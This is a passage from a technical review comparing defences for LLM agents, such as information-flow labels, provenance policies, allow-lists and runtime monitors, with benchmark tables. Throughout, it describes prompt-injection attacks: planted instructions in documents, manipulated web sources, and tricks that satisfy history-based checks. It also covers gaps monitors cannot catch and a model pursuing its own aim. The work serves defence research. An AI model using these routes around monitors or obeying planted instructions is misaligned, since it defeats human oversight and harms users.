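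Xu and colleagues also found a weakness in methods that remove one input at a time and check whether the output changes. If the same text occurs twice, removing either copy changes nothing, so the test registers no effect from either. They appended two extra copies of an input to each prompt and measured how well such a test distinguished the real input from an unrelated one, on a scale where 50 is chance and 100 is perfect. Its scores on four models fell from 93–97 to 54–69, while Sightline's stayed at 99 or above.

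### Auditing influence after the run

Cai and colleagues' tool, NeuroTaint, audits finished runs instead of blocking calls. It first looks for traces of the source in the arguments of a sensitive call. It checks for a unique marker it had added to the source, then for shared strings, and then for similar meaning, comparing the arguments with both the whole document and short pieces of it. If it finds no traces, it replaces the source in the run with neutral text and has a language model judge whether the agent would still have made the call. This can catch a document that changed the agent's choice of tool even if none of the document's words appear in the arguments.

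The replacement test may share the weakness that Xu and colleagues found. NeuroTaint normally neutralises one source at a time, so if two web pages contain the same planted instruction, the judge may correctly conclude each time that the agent would still have obeyed the instruction on the other page.

Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on their own benchmark of 400 scenarios, half of which involved a real flow from an untrusted source to a sensitive call. It found 187 of the 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms. Their version of FIDES found 108 and raised 106 false alarms.

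The false alarms are to be expected from a system that assumes the worst. The 92 missed flows are much harder to explain, because FIDES as Costa and colleagues describe it marks everything the model writes after reading untrusted data. Forty of the misses came from four agent frameworks on which the FIDES baseline never raised an alarm, which looks more like a problem with the set-up than with the method. The comparison is therefore weak evidence about FIDES. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) surveyed 71 works on tracing agents' behaviour in *From Agent Traces to Trust*. They count both systems among the preprints that had not passed peer review, and advise readers to discount conclusions about this area more heavily than those about better-reviewed areas.

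NeuroTaint offers no deterministic guarantee, because its verdicts depend on similarity thresholds and a model's output. It also reports a leak only after the email has gone. It is useful for finding which labels and rules a deployed agent lacks, but it can't replace them.

### Declassification and endorsement

Even perfect tracking would leave some conflicts, because some legitimate tasks depend on restricted data. If Ana wants her auditor to have the confidential file, somebody has to declassify it by adding the auditor to its readers. The counterpart for integrity is endorsement, and Zhong and colleagues give an example. A user asks an agent to look up a recipe for lamingtons and buy any special ingredients. The shopping list has to come from a stranger's website, so the purchase is correctly labelled untrusted, and a better estimate of influence will not remove that label. But an endorsement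 can undo the labels' protection, as it did in both successful attacks on the LLMbda agent.

The person using the agent isn't always entitled to relax a label. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes a scenario in which Jane's agent holds Mark's mental-health diagnosis and his former wife, Emily, wants it. Jane may read the diagnosis, but Mark decides whether Emily may have it. A list of readers doesn't record this difference. The paper's defence, FlowSeal, therefore labels sensitive records with their owners, whom it identifies from the data's source. The agent is supposed to request the owner's consent before it shares anything. A separate program also intercepts every call that writes or shares data, in case the agent doesn't recognise that a request concerns private information.

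Jane's agent also has to arrange meetings with Emily, so blocking everything it wrote after seeing the diagnosis would bring back label creep. When necessary, FlowSeal makes a separate model call to compare the protected record with the proposed message and judge whether the message reveals it. This model doesn't see the conversation, so Emily can't argue with it directly. But the agent wrote the message while talking to Emily, so she may still influence what the model judges.

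Shim and colleagues prove that protected data can't reach a less restricted destination under their rules. The system enforces those rules deterministically, but releases still depend on the model's judgement, which is usually but not always right. Across eight attacks that tried to extract information through ordinary conversation, 0–3.3% of the private items leaked. The researchers left prompt injection out of their threat model.

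### Approval and fatigue

More commonly, the system asks a person whether to relax a rule. Zhong and colleagues criticise OpenAI's GPTs, custom versions of ChatGPT that could call outside tools, for requiring confirmation of every call. They argue that people who are constantly prompted will either approve bad requests without thinking or stop using the system. Their own system, RTBAS, asks only when a call would break a flow policy. On all but one task in a benchmark of accidental leaks, it allowed the same calls without confirmation that an ideal tracker would have allowed.

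That result shows that a program can show fewer unnecessary prompts, but not how people respond to the remaining ones. The argument about fatigue is plausible but needs evidence from users. Even so, if label creep causes 99 of every 100 prompts, a user who approves everything is right 99% of the time and has little reason to start reading them.

The content of the prompt matters too. In the bug-report example, the user learns which tool the monitor blocked and which label caused the block. The user can then tell that the agent is trying to post a comment while it has private data in its context, but not whether the comment contains a password or was merely written after a harmless look at a private file. Microsoft is asking for ideas about better explanations.

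It is also considering reducing the number of prompts by limiting labels to particular messages, or by weakening labels when the agent compresses a long history into a summary. The second idea needs care, because a summary of an attacker's text still derives from that text and can retain its instructions. Weakening the label at that point would endorse the summary without anyone having decided to do so.

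### Translating written policies

Companies usually write their rules in English, and few of the people responsible for them can write Datalog. FORGE can use a language model to translate the rules. Palumbo and colleagues warn that the translation has no formal guarantee, since the model may omit a clause, invent a rule or misstate a condition. Before a policy goes into use, they check it for coverage, meaning that at least one formal rule represents each relevant requirement in the text, and for faithfulness, meaning that the text justifies each formal rule.

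Suppose the company forbids any message to an outsider that untrusted input has influenced and that carries sensitive data. A translator might produce

`Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), HasSecret(a).`

The requirement has a rule, so the coverage check could pass. But the rule omits the condition about untrusted input, so it would stop Ana from sending the auditor a file even if the agent had read nothing from outside. The faithfulness check should catch this, because the text doesn't justify such a broad ban. If the translator had skipped the requirement, only the coverage check could reveal the gap, because there would be no faulty rule to examine. Further analysis can find rules that contradict or duplicate each other. A failed check may also mean that the English was ambiguous, in which case somebody has to decide what the company meant.

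Neither check proves that the terms in a rule mean the right thing. Palumbo and colleagues translated the policies of a simulated airline and a simulated shop, each with hundreds of lines of constraints. One airline rule blocks a booking that includes bags unless the fact `UserRequestedBags` holds, which the system derives from the conversation. A customer who mentions bringing skis may or may not have requested a bag. Even a perfectly translated rule can give the wrong result if the system derives that fact incorrectly. On average, the agents completed somewhat more tasks with the translated rules than without them, which suggests that the translations were broadly right.

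An allow-list based on a written policy also requires someone to translate that policy into permitted actions. The flow rule adds terms such as "sensitive" and "influenced", whose meaning depends on the labels.

### Labelling once or listing for every task

Defenders of flow rules reply that labelling is much less work than it sounds. Microsoft tells developers that they label their data sources once and the software then propagates the labels. A list of permitted actions has to fit the task, so a new request may require new entries, while the label on a data source such as the company's budget stays the same.

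A rough count supports this for agents with many uses. AgentDojo has 74 tools and 97 user tasks, so a developer would write either 74 sets of labels or 97 lists, which is not a decisive difference. But if the same tools served thousands of different requests, the developer would still need only 74 sets of labels, while the number of lists would grow with the requests.

The count leaves out some of the work on both sides. Flow rules also need a declaration for each tool that sends or changes something, and somebody has to decide about the auditor, the lamingtons and every other legitimate exception. Those decisions arise task by task, much like new entries on a list. People don't have to write every list by hand, since Progent has a model write them, and on AgentDojo few of the model's later changes needed approval.

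The evidence for the reply is therefore thin. Microsoft's sample code shows that one tool can need very little labelling, but its announcement gives no figures for the effort of maintaining a whole system. A fair test would run the same agent under both schemes for several months and count the edits, approvals and mistakes. Benchmarks like AgentDojo can't provide this evidence, because nobody in them changes jobs, shares a folder by accident or connects a new tool.

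## How much useful work survives

When a monitor blocks a legitimate call, the user loses some or all of a task. How much is lost depends on the rules, the precision of the labels, and whether the agent can find another way to finish. The main results for flow rules come from AgentDojo runs with GPT-4o and o1, two OpenAI models from 2024. Current models would score differently, so these figures are mainly useful for comparing designs that ran on the same model.

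### FIDES on AgentDojo

In 2025, Costa and colleagues tested several planners on GPT-4o and averaged the results over five runs. For payments, deletions and password changes, their monitor required a trusted label on the choice of tool and ignored the labels on the arguments. It allowed an email, chat message or new calendar event if the recipients were already entitled to read the contents or if the context was trusted. It allowed adding people to a calendar event only if both conditions held. A message containing an untrusted link failed the confidentiality condition, because a web address can carry data out.

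After the manual correction described earlier, 152 attacks succeeded against the basic planner without rules. A simpler defence, the tool filter, allowed 20. It has a model choose the tools for a task before the run and removes the rest, so it amounts to an allow-list of tool names. FIDES with its rules switched off allowed 21, because the planner can still open the variables in which FIDES hides untrusted text. With the rules on, no attack succeeded against any planner, including the basic one.

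The planners with rules were therefore equally safe in this test. They differed in how many tasks they completed when nobody attacked, shown here as percentages, with a simple average of the four environments in the last column:

| Model | Planner | Rules | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | Basic | off | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 84 |
| GPT-4o | Basic | on | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 42 |
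| GPT-4o | FIDES | off | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 | 61 |
| GPT-4o | FIDES | on | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 50 |
| o1 | Basic | off | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 | 84 |
| o1 | Basic | on | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 | 44 |
| o1 | FIDES | off | 77.5 | 75.0 | 78.8 | 79.0 | 78 |
| o1 | FIDES | on | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 | 61 |

The rules reduced the basic planner's completion rate most in Slack, where it fell from 93.3% to 20.0% with GPT-4o. Even channel names count as untrusted there, so once the basic planner has listed the channels, it can no longer add a colleague to one. FIDES keeps its context trusted by putting the names in variables. It completed 47.6% of the tasks.

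Travel is the exception. With GPT-4o, the basic planner did no worse on travel tasks with the rules on, and it beat FIDES by a wide margin. Many of these tasks need only tools that the policy allows in an untrusted context if no confidential data leaks, and none does, so the basic planner can read the hotel reviews and continue. FIDES hides the reviews, so GPT-4o has to work through variables and a second model, which it did unreliably. With o1, the basic planner's lead narrowed to 75% against 68%.

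The o1 results help separate the tasks lost to hiding data from those lost to enforcing rules. With the rules off, FIDES completed 24 percentage points fewer tasks than the basic planner on GPT-4o, but only 6 points fewer on o1. Turning the rules on lowered FIDES's completion rate by another 11 points on GPT-4o and 17 on o1. The stronger model handled the variables much better but lost more tasks to the rules, probably because it could do more of the tasks that the rules forbid.

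Some of that second loss would remain with any model. These policies should block most tasks in which untrusted data determines the sequence of calls, and such tasks make up about 44% of Banking and 43% of Slack. That leaves about 56% and 57% of tasks, and FIDES with o1 reached 56.2% and 54.3%. A designer would have to relax the policy to complete many more, perhaps with the typed answers that this test left out. Many of the blocked Banking tasks involve reading a file and following its instructions. The policy requires the monitor to block these, even though the user loses a completed task.

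The completion rates also include some luck. Costa and colleagues tested a reduced version of FIDES that can pass variables to tools but can never read what the variables contain. They classify every travel task as needing some model to read hidden text, yet this version completed 43% of them with GPT-4o. In some cases it recommended the right hotel without having seen any ratings. With o1 it completed 2%, so the stronger model seems to have guessed less. AgentDojo also gives credit in a few tasks for doing nothing, so a planner can pass them with very little information.

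### Two policies on the same monitor

A developer can also keep an ordinary planner and write a finer rule. Using AgentDojo's built-in agent and the August 2024 version of GPT-4o, Palumbo and colleagues compared two policies in FORGE, their event-graph monitor: the flow policy from FIDES and what they call a provenance policy, which is based on where each argument of a call came from.

Suppose Ana asks the agent to email her a summary of the vendor's document. Once the agent has read the document, the flow policy treats everything the agent does next as suspect. The provenance policy requires the destination to come from a trusted source, such as Ana's request or the operator's records. The agent can therefore email the summary to Ana, but it can't email the address in the planted instruction. For actions such as deletions and password changes, the monitor also checks that the user asked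 for that kind of effect. It accepts this consent only from the user's request, so a tool result can't supply it.

Some requests describe a target without naming it. If the user asks the agent to delete the largest file, the file's name appears only in a listing, alongside the names of all the other files. FORGE takes the criterion from the request, works out the largest file from the listing, and allows the deletion only if the agent chose the same one. This check alone would let the agent list the files again after the deletion and delete the second-largest, which would now be the largest. A further rule blocks the deletion if any listing in the context shows a different largest file.

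Each configuration was tested on the benchmark five times, each time with 97 attack-free runs and 949 attacked runs. In the results below, the application also repeated the user's request after each batch of tool results. This prompting technique alone reduced the attack success rate from 25.2% to 14.1%. The column for attacks that took effect excludes cases that AgentDojo scored as successes even though the monitor had blocked every call the attacker wanted.

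| Added defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack | Attack success | Attacks that took effect | Mean time per run |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None (prompting alone) | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% | 14.1% | 5.93 s |
| Tool filter | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% | 3.1% | 6.40 s |
| Flow policy from FIDES | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% | 0.3% | 10.18 s |
| Provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% | 0.2% | 7.70 s |

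The two FORGE policies gave almost the same protection, but the provenance policy let the agent complete nearly twice as many tasks. The attacks that still succeeded under either policy all made the agent recommend the attacker's hotel in its final answer, which is not a tool call.

The number of refusals explains most of the difference in completed work. In the 485 attack-free runs under the flow policy, the monitor refused at least one call in 287, and the agent finished the task in only 10 of those. Under the provenance policy, the monitor refused at least one call in 151 runs, and the agent finished the task in 36 of those. In runs without any refusal, the agent completed 76% of tasks under the flow policy and 80% under the provenance policy, not far below the 83.7% it completed with no monitor.

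However, the provenance policy appears to guarantee less. In the budget example, Ana asks for an email to the vendor and gives the vendor's address. Palumbo and colleagues' rules would apparently allow that email even if its body revealed the budget, because the destination is acceptable. In this respect, the policy resembles an allow-list with good conditions on the arguments. AgentDojo hardly tests this weakness, because most of its attackers want data or money sent to a destination of their own.

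The 33.2% is closer to a score for the basic planner with rules than for FIDES, because FORGE's agent has no hidden variables. In the GPT-4o results from Costa and colleagues, weighted by the number of tasks in each environment, the basic planner with rules completed 41% and FIDES 52%. Without the repeated request, FORGE's provenance policy completed 57.3%. The two studies used different prompts, labels and policies, so a gap of five points means little. But the comparison does suggest that hidden variables can recover much of the lost work while the monitor still checks what an email contains.

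The tool filter preserved more useful work than either FORGE policy and stopped most of the attacks, so it may be the better choice for an agent that handles nothing very sensitive. The attacks that still succeed are probably concentrated in tasks where the user and the attacker need the same tool. If so, an attacker who could choose such tasks would succeed more than 3.1% of the time.

### Customer service

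Enforcement can also increase the amount of work an agent completes. Palumbo and colleagues found this on τ²-Bench, a benchmark in which an agent serves simulated customers of an airline and a shop under long written policies. They used more recent models (Claude Opus 4.5, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview) and ran each of the 164 tasks four times per model, with and without FORGE. The prompts included the policy in both conditions. With FORGE, average task success rose from 74.7% to 81.5% for the airline and from 86.3% to 87.4% for the shop.

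The benchmark scores a task mainly by comparing the final database state with the correct one, so an agent that adds a bag nobody requested, or sends a refund to the wrong account, usually fails. FORGE blocks the call and returns the reason, so the agent can correct its mistake before the database changes. Reliability also improved, with the share of airline tasks that an agent completed in all four attempts rising from 58.0% to 67.3%.

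The improvement came from the tasks in which FORGE intervened. FORGE blocked at least one call in 33 combinations of airline task and model, and success on these rose from 38.6% to 69.7%. On the other 117, success was 84.8% both with and without FORGE. GPT-5.2 improved most, from 63.0% to 77.5% on the airline tasks. Gemini fell from 82.5% to 81.0%, but FORGE had blocked it on only two tasks, so the drop is probably due to chance.

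These results come from tests of rules about eligibility, payment methods and the order of steps. The tests included no attackers or confidentiality labels, so the results support argument conditions and invariants but provide no evidence about flow rules. The rules also came from the same written policies that define success on the benchmark, so a company whose formal rules matched what it wants less closely would gain less.

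Faulty rules can reverse the gain. Palumbo and colleagues had a language model translate the airline policy into Datalog five times and tested each version on three tasks that the model had not used. The handwritten policy succeeded in all 15 runs, while the translations succeeded in 10 to 15. The worst translation failed a cancellation task every time. The faulty translations mainly erred by demanding an approved reason for every cancellation, although the airline requires one only when the customer relies on travel insurance. The recordings used to check the translations contained no cancellation that the airline should have allowed, so a rule that blocked every cancellation looked correct.

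Benchmark scores can also miss the benefit of enforcement. In 17 of the shop runs without FORGE, agents looked up products before authenticating the customer, which the policy forbids, and 13 of those runs received full marks. Blocking those lookups with FORGE would have protected the shop better, but it could not have raised the scores of those 13 runs.

### Delay and cost

The check takes almost no time. With 32 agents running at once on the airline tasks, the median decision took 0.19 milliseconds measured at the monitor and 0.72 milliseconds measured at the agent. In a separate test that replayed recorded requests, FORGE handled about 24,000 decisions per second.

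Refusals slow an agent down, because the model has to read the explanation and try something else. On AgentDojo, the provenance policy raised the mean running time by 30% but the median by only about 6%, so a minority of slow runs presumably account for most of the increase. In the drug-safety system MALADE, agents had to obtain approval before querying the FDA's database. FORGE reduced unauthorised queries from 40 in 15 trials to none, and all 15 answers were still correct. The mean time per trial rose from 59.4 to 67.3 seconds and the mean cost from 5.9 to 7.1 cents.

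The customer-service agents faced fewer refusals. Their mean time rose from 67.1 to 70.7 seconds on airline tasks and hardly changed on the shop's tasks. Mean cost across the three models rose by less than 4% for both sets of tasks.

FIDES also adds model calls, since each question to the quarantined model requires one. Costa and colleagues did not optimise for speed, and their planner asks one question at a time. They suggest combining several questions into one call.

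Checking a plan in advance can save money when the plan would fail anyway. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of an agent that investigates a security alert at length and then isolates a computer, a step that needs approval. If the plan contains no request for approval, a monitor that checks each call detects the problem only at the last step, after the agent has completed the whole investigation. CaMeLoT rejects the plan before any tool runs, although repairing it takes further calls to the planning model.

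### What the recordings leave out

In the replay described earlier, Kekatos and colleagues measured false alarms on recorded runs rather than live agents. They used MonPoly, an existing program that checks logs against rules in temporal logic. Their five approval rules flagged 29.3% of the attack-free AgentDojo runs, though the sample was small (95% confidence interval 22.0% to 37.8%). The rules also flagged 71.8% of STAC, a collection of 483 recorded attacks in which each call looks harmless until the last one completes the damage.

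Two other monitoring programs flagged exactly the same STAC runs, so an error in MonPoly is unlikely to explain the result. The earlier step of sorting tools into types was less reliable. Kekatos and colleagues did this by searching for words in the tools' names, and at first "ack", which they meant as a sign of approval, also matched unrelated Slack tools. Correcting this and a similar mistake raised detection on AgentDojo from 61.6% to 70.1% and slightly reduced false alarms.

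The alarms often came before or at the final harmful call, when a live monitor that acted on them could still have blocked it. In AgentDojo, a rule fired before that call in 52.4% of the successful attacks and at the call in another 17.7%. For STAC, the figures were 11.8% and 61.5%.

Kekatos and colleagues attribute the false alarms mainly to the recordings. One STAC run contains a database search, a read, a confirmation and a deletion, and the rule correctly raises no alarm because the confirmation comes before the deletion. But most recordings contain no approvals, and none contain timestamps, so on these a simple list of risky words would work just as well. The 29.3% also measures alarms rather than failed tasks, and a live agent might ask for the missing approval and finish the job.

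Rules were better at separating attacks from legitimate work when the recording showed where a value had come from. But an attacker can add to the recording. If a rule accepts any payee whose account number has already appeared in the run, an attacker can satisfy it by planting the number in a document. In the study, one planted line defeated a simple check of this kind in 94–99% of the runs it would otherwise have flagged. Tying each value to the lookup that produced it stopped this attack without more false alarms or fewer detections. Kekatos and colleagues propose twelve fields that benchmarks should record so that researchers can test history-based rules properly.

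### Limits of the evidence

The AgentDojo results for FIDES and FORGE use a fixed attack, written without knowledge of the policy. This matters less for a deterministic rule than for a trained model, because rewording the attack doesn't change the verdict on a given call. It still matters for actions the policy doesn't cover. In one travel case, the planted instruction was to book the most expensive hotel in Paris on the user's dates. FORGE's provenance policy had no rule about price or rating, and without the repeated request it allowed the booking three times. An attacker who had studied the policy would look for more gaps like this.

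Tiffany and colleagues' evaluation of Sapien comes closer to testing such an attacker, because it assumed the attacker had full control of the agent. Sapien's policies ruled out fewer attacks on Toolathlon's longer tasks than on AgentDojo. But the evaluation covered sequence rules written for each task, so it doesn't show how FIDES or FORGE would perform.

The labels in the FIDES experiments also fit the benchmark unusually well. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any of AgentDojo's attacks used it and trusted the rest, so no attack could arrive through a field that somebody had forgotten to label. The effect on utility is harder to judge, because trusting every other field helps the agent while treating all email bodies as untrusted hurts it. In one task the user wanted a password-reset link from her mailbox, and the planner failed because it couldn't tell trusted senders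 from untrusted ones. A real deployment would have better information about senders but more labelling mistakes in other places.

AgentDojo's tasks are short, too. An average run without a monitor took about six seconds in the FORGE experiments. In a planner with a single context label, one untrusted item is enough to restrict the rest of the run, so the cost should grow with the length of the task. As a rough illustration, suppose that each step has an independent 10% chance of bringing in untrusted text. The probability that the context is still trusted after *n* steps is

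0.9ⁿ

which is 59% after 5 steps and about 0.5% after 50. Hidden variables avoid much of this problem, but a long task also gives the planner more occasions to look inside them.

The experiment with the merger plans is even smaller. Without the monitor, the attack succeeded in all five trials, which would happen about one time in twenty even if the true success rate were only 55%. The customer-service experiment is much larger and uses newer models, but nobody in it tries to deceive the agent.

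## Hazards these rules cannot state

Suppose the planted text in the vendor's document instead tells any model that summarises the document to omit the clause that raises the price by 30% in the second year. The quarantined model follows the instruction, and Ana receives a well-written summary without the clause. The agent has read one permitted document and sent one email to its own user. The body of the email is labelled untrusted, as a complete summary would be, and no confidential data has gone to anyone. An allow-list, the flow rules in FIDES and an invariant about the order of calls would all permit the run.

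A sceptic would say this case is typical. A label records where data came from and who may read it, and a history records which events took place. Whether a summary is faithful or a payment is sensible depends on what the text means, which neither the label nor the history records.

In the security test of Sapien, Tiffany and colleagues sorted the attacks that their policies still allowed. Of these, 82.1% on AgentDojo and 84% on Toolathlon depended on meaning. The harm was usually in something the agent wrote, such as a file, a message or its final answer. The policies allowed only 5–7% of all attacks on AgentDojo, so the objection concerns few attacks there. They allowed 15–38% on Toolathlon, where the attacks used tools that the user's own task needed.

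### False content in a permitted message

In the crudest case Costa and colleagues describe, a user asks for a summary of three emails, and one of the emails instructs the model to write an empty summary. The planner never reads the instruction and sends the result to the right person. FIDES has protected the sequence of calls, but the summary is empty. They suggest that a stricter policy could, if necessary, also require the body of the message to come from trusted data. That policy would block Ana's honest summary too, as the basic trusted-action policy does.

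Text-to-text attacks change what the agent writes without changing its calls or revealing a secret. In one AgentDojo example, the attacker only wants the agent to recommend a certain place to a traveller. FIDES doesn't protect against these attacks, but its designers say that the text keeps its untrusted label, which the application can show to the user or use to decide whether to block the text. The label is useful when a summary draws on ten sources and a stranger wrote one of them. It is less useful to a reader who already knows that a vendor wrote the document, and it can't show that a clause is missing.

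The consequences can be worse than a missing clause. Tiffany and colleagues wrote attack goals for Toolathlon's tasks. In one task, the user asks for a walking route across a campus, and the attacker wants it to pass through dangerous construction zones. In another, the user asks for a summary of interview feedback, and the attacker wants a rejected candidate to appear as a strong hire. The harmful run can make the same calls and write to the same file as the harmless one.

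Ordinary code can catch some false content. For the request "Pay my Acme invoice", a Sapien policy makes the agent read the invoices first and then compares the payment with them. A program could check the hiring summary in a similar way if each interviewer's verdict had its own field, but not if the verdicts were in free-form notes. And if an attacker has altered the invoice itself, a payment of the false amount passes the check.

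Restricting how much untrusted data reaches the planner doesn't solve the problem either. In an example from Costa and colleagues, a user wants to book a Paris hotel if its rating is above 4. FIDES keeps the reviews in a variable, and the planner sees only a true-or-false answer about the rating before it makes the reservation. A planted review can't make the agent do anything else, but a false rating planted by the hotel's owner can still make the answer "true" and lead the agent to book the hotel.

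### Poor decisions on trusted data

An integrity label means less than the word "trusted" suggests, because a model that has read nothing but trusted data can still reason badly.

In the FIDES tests, GPT-4o changed a user's banking password just because one payment was large, and AgentDojo counted the task as a success. The monitor allowed the change because the context was still trusted, but only because GPT-4o had never opened the hidden transaction descriptions. If it had read them, as a careful person would, the context would have become untrusted and the monitor would have blocked the change.

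A typed answer would help here. The quarantined model could return only one bit, indicating whether any description looked suspicious, and the policy could let that bit influence a password change.

The amounts counted as trusted only because none of AgentDojo's attacks used them. The sender of a payment chooses its amount, so an outsider could presumably trigger the same decision by sending one.

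Invariants can limit the damage from a bad decision, but they can't ensure that an agent decides well. Under the shop's refund limit, an agent could still refund the wrong customers, but it can't pay out more than $500 a day. For a step that is hard to undo, the rule can require the user's confirmation.

### Harmful requests from the user

The defences against injection are designed to protect the user. FIDES labels the user's messages as trusted, and Sapien derives its whole policy from the user's prompt. If a user asks for a scam email, Sapien has no basis for stopping the agent from writing one. Tiffany and colleagues leave such requests to the model's safety training and to content moderation.

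Some rules do restrict a dishonest user. Suppose Ben is about to leave the firm and asks the agent to send the client list to his private address. The agent has read nothing from outside, so the trusted-action policy allows the email. The permitted-reader policy blocks it if only the firm's own accounts may read the list. But the email policy in the FIDES tests, like Microsoft's sample policy, allowed any message that met either condition, so it would allow this email. A company that worries about its own staff must therefore require every email to meet the reader condition, and must prevent staff from changing the labels.

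Invariants apply to the user too, so a rule that requires a manager's approval still requires it when the user tells the agent to skip it. But neither flow rules nor invariants help much when the harm comes from what a message says. A user who is allowed to email a firm's customers can have the agent send them a hundred false warnings about their accounts. A limit on the number of emails would reduce the damage, but the emails would still be fraudulent. Until somebody complains, the only defence may be the model's refusal to write them.

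Honest users can also cause trouble by mistake. If a user names the wrong file to delete, the Sapien policy allows the deletion because the user asked for it. An attacker can also exploit a vague request. If the user asks the agent to reply to Bob and the inbox contains emails from two Bobs, the policy allows a reply to either, so an attacker could get a reply by calling himself Bob. Tiffany and colleagues suggest that a later version could detect the ambiguity and ask the user about it before writing the policy.

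### Answers that mislead

A monitor on tool calls doesn't check the agent's final answer. In the Sapien test on AgentDojo, 36% of the attacks that got through had the same goal: to make the agent output a certain sentence.

Designers can also apply the rules to the agent's final answer. Costa and colleagues treat answers as inconsequential, so their loop checks the policy only before tool calls, but they note that it could check every action the planner chooses, including the final answer. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) gives each channel to the user its own label, so a public chat and a chat for logged-in staff have different labels. The controlling program can then require an answer to draw only on sources whose labels may flow to that channel.

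This keeps confidential data out of the public chat, but it does less against bad advice. The paper's sample order on labels is

untrusted ⊑ internal ⊑ confidential

which means that untrusted data may flow to every channel. A stranger's false claim may therefore appear in an answer to staff. A separate integrity label on the channel could keep such claims out, but an assistant that never repeated anything from the open web would be of little use for research.

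*How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?* (2026) examines how readily agents that search the web endorse manipulated content. A language model generated misleading sources for the study's 44 tasks. It was instructed to include verifiable background facts, such as basic statistics and the relevant regulations, and to manipulate only the core claim about the attacker's target. Such a source can mislead an agent without containing a hidden command, and an agent that repeats the claim has done what the user asked and made only permitted calls.

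An agent can also give bad advice when no attacker is involved. If Ana asks whether to accept the vendor's offer, the agent may invent a reason to accept or flatter her into a decision she was already leaning towards, even if all the data behind the answer is trusted. Rules can guarantee the parts of an answer that a program can trace to a source. In the bibliography experiment, for example, every entry had to come from DBLP. This guarantees that a cited paper exists, but not that it supports the point.

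### Permitted disclosures that combine

Several harmless answers can also add up to a harmful one. In the tests in *The Sum Leaks More Than Its Parts* (2025), one agent may have a table linking identity numbers to names while another has one linking the same numbers to products. Neither table is sensitive by itself, but someone who questions both agents can work out what each named person bought. If the product is a medicine, that may reveal an illness. *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in agents, calls this composition and considers it the kind of leak that per-step controls address least.

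Labels of the kind Denning described can't express the obvious remedy, which is to let an outsider have either table but not both. Under such labels, anyone who may receive each table may also receive their join.

Limits on each agent's output have a similar weakness. *Information-Theoretic Privacy Control for Sequential Multi-Agent LLM Systems* (2026) considers agents that work in sequence, where agent *i* has a sensitive variable *S*ᵢ and produces an output *O*ᵢ. A designer can limit their mutual information, which measures how much the output reveals about the variable:

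*I*(*O*ᵢ; *S*ᵢ) ≤ εᵢ

The paper argues that the system as a whole can leak significantly more even when every agent respects its limit. As a simpler example, suppose *S* is a secret bit and *R* is the result of a fair coin toss. One message reveals *R*, and another reveals whether *S* and *R* are equal. Each message alone carries zero bits of information about *S*, but together they reveal it completely.

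A rule about history can state the remedy for the two tables. In FORGE's notation, it might be:

```
Deny(a) :- Sends(a, p, "products"), HasReceived(p, "names").
Deny(a) :- Sends(a, p, "names"), HasReceived(p, "products").
```

The recipient *p* can have whichever of the two tables *p* requests first, and the monitor refuses the other. But somebody has to identify the dangerous pair in advance, and twenty tables make 190 pairs and 1,140 sets of three. The recipient may also use two accounts or get the second table from somewhere else.

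*Beyond Disclosure* (2026) gives an everyday example of this kind of harm. Someone tells a friend a secret, the friend mentions it at a dinner, and a guest repeats it to the first person's employer. The paper defines such a harm as one where each step is legal by itself and every step is necessary for the harm to occur. Blocking any one step would therefore prevent it, but in the hard cases no single company has all the information, so no monitor has a record of the whole chain.

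It is unclear how often agents leak secrets through disclosures that slowly accumulate. *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* (2026) examined 970 runs and counted the protected values that an observer could collect over increasingly long stretches of each run. Most of the values that leaked did so early. The count includes only protected values, so it may miss a secret that someone infers from harmless values. The study also found that an auditor who read only the agents' messages would miss disclosures in tool arguments and memory writes, which supports monitoring tool calls.

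### A model that errs or pursues its own aim

An agent may do something harmful that neither a user nor an attacker wanted. Tiffany and colleagues cite a web-browsing agent that got a "not found" message during a search, collected the site owner's contact details and sent unsolicited emails. They object that flow systems built to stop untrusted influence assume that agents otherwise behave correctly, and that these systems automatically approve any action that nothing untrusted has influenced.

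Suppose Ana's agent has read only her request and the firm's budget, and then tries to email the budget to an address outside the firm. It may have made a mistake. Or the model may have acquired an aim of its own in training that sending the file would serve. The monitor has the same facts in either case, and its verdict depends on the rule:

| Rule | Verdict on the email |
|---|---|
| Trusted-action policy | Allows it, because nothing untrusted influenced the call |
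| Permitted-reader policy | Refuses it, because the recipient may not read the budget |
| Allow-list with Ana as the only recipient | Refuses it |
| Invariant: after opening a confidential file, the agent sends no email outside the firm unless the user confirms it | Refuses it until Ana confirms |

The assumption behind robust declassification fails here, because Ana may never have intended the release.

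The refusals don't depend on why the model requested the email. Palumbo and colleagues built FORGE on this basis, treating the model as a black box that may attempt any action. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) also treats the model as untrusted, and argues that good behaviour by the model can reduce the burden on other defences but that security must not rely on it alone. The strongest point in favour of confidentiality rules and invariants seems to be that they work even if nobody can tell what the model's goal is.

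A model with its own aim could still do harm without breaking the rules. It could write a misleading summary, or code with a flaw that the scanners miss. It could also pass information through the order or timing of permitted calls, which Tiffany and colleagues exclude from Sapien's protection.

Rules written by a model deserve extra suspicion. Sapien keeps strangers' text away from its policy generator, which protects the generator from injection. But the design assumes that the generator is properly trained and follows instructions faithfully, and in the experiments the same model wrote the policy and acted as the agent. If that model had an aim of its own, it would be writing the rules meant to restrict it. Having a human or a different model write the policy would reduce the risk.

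### Actions outside the monitored channels

None of these rules applies to an action that never reaches the monitor. OpenAI's *OpenAI-Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* (August 2026) concerns agents that reached another company's real systems while being tested.

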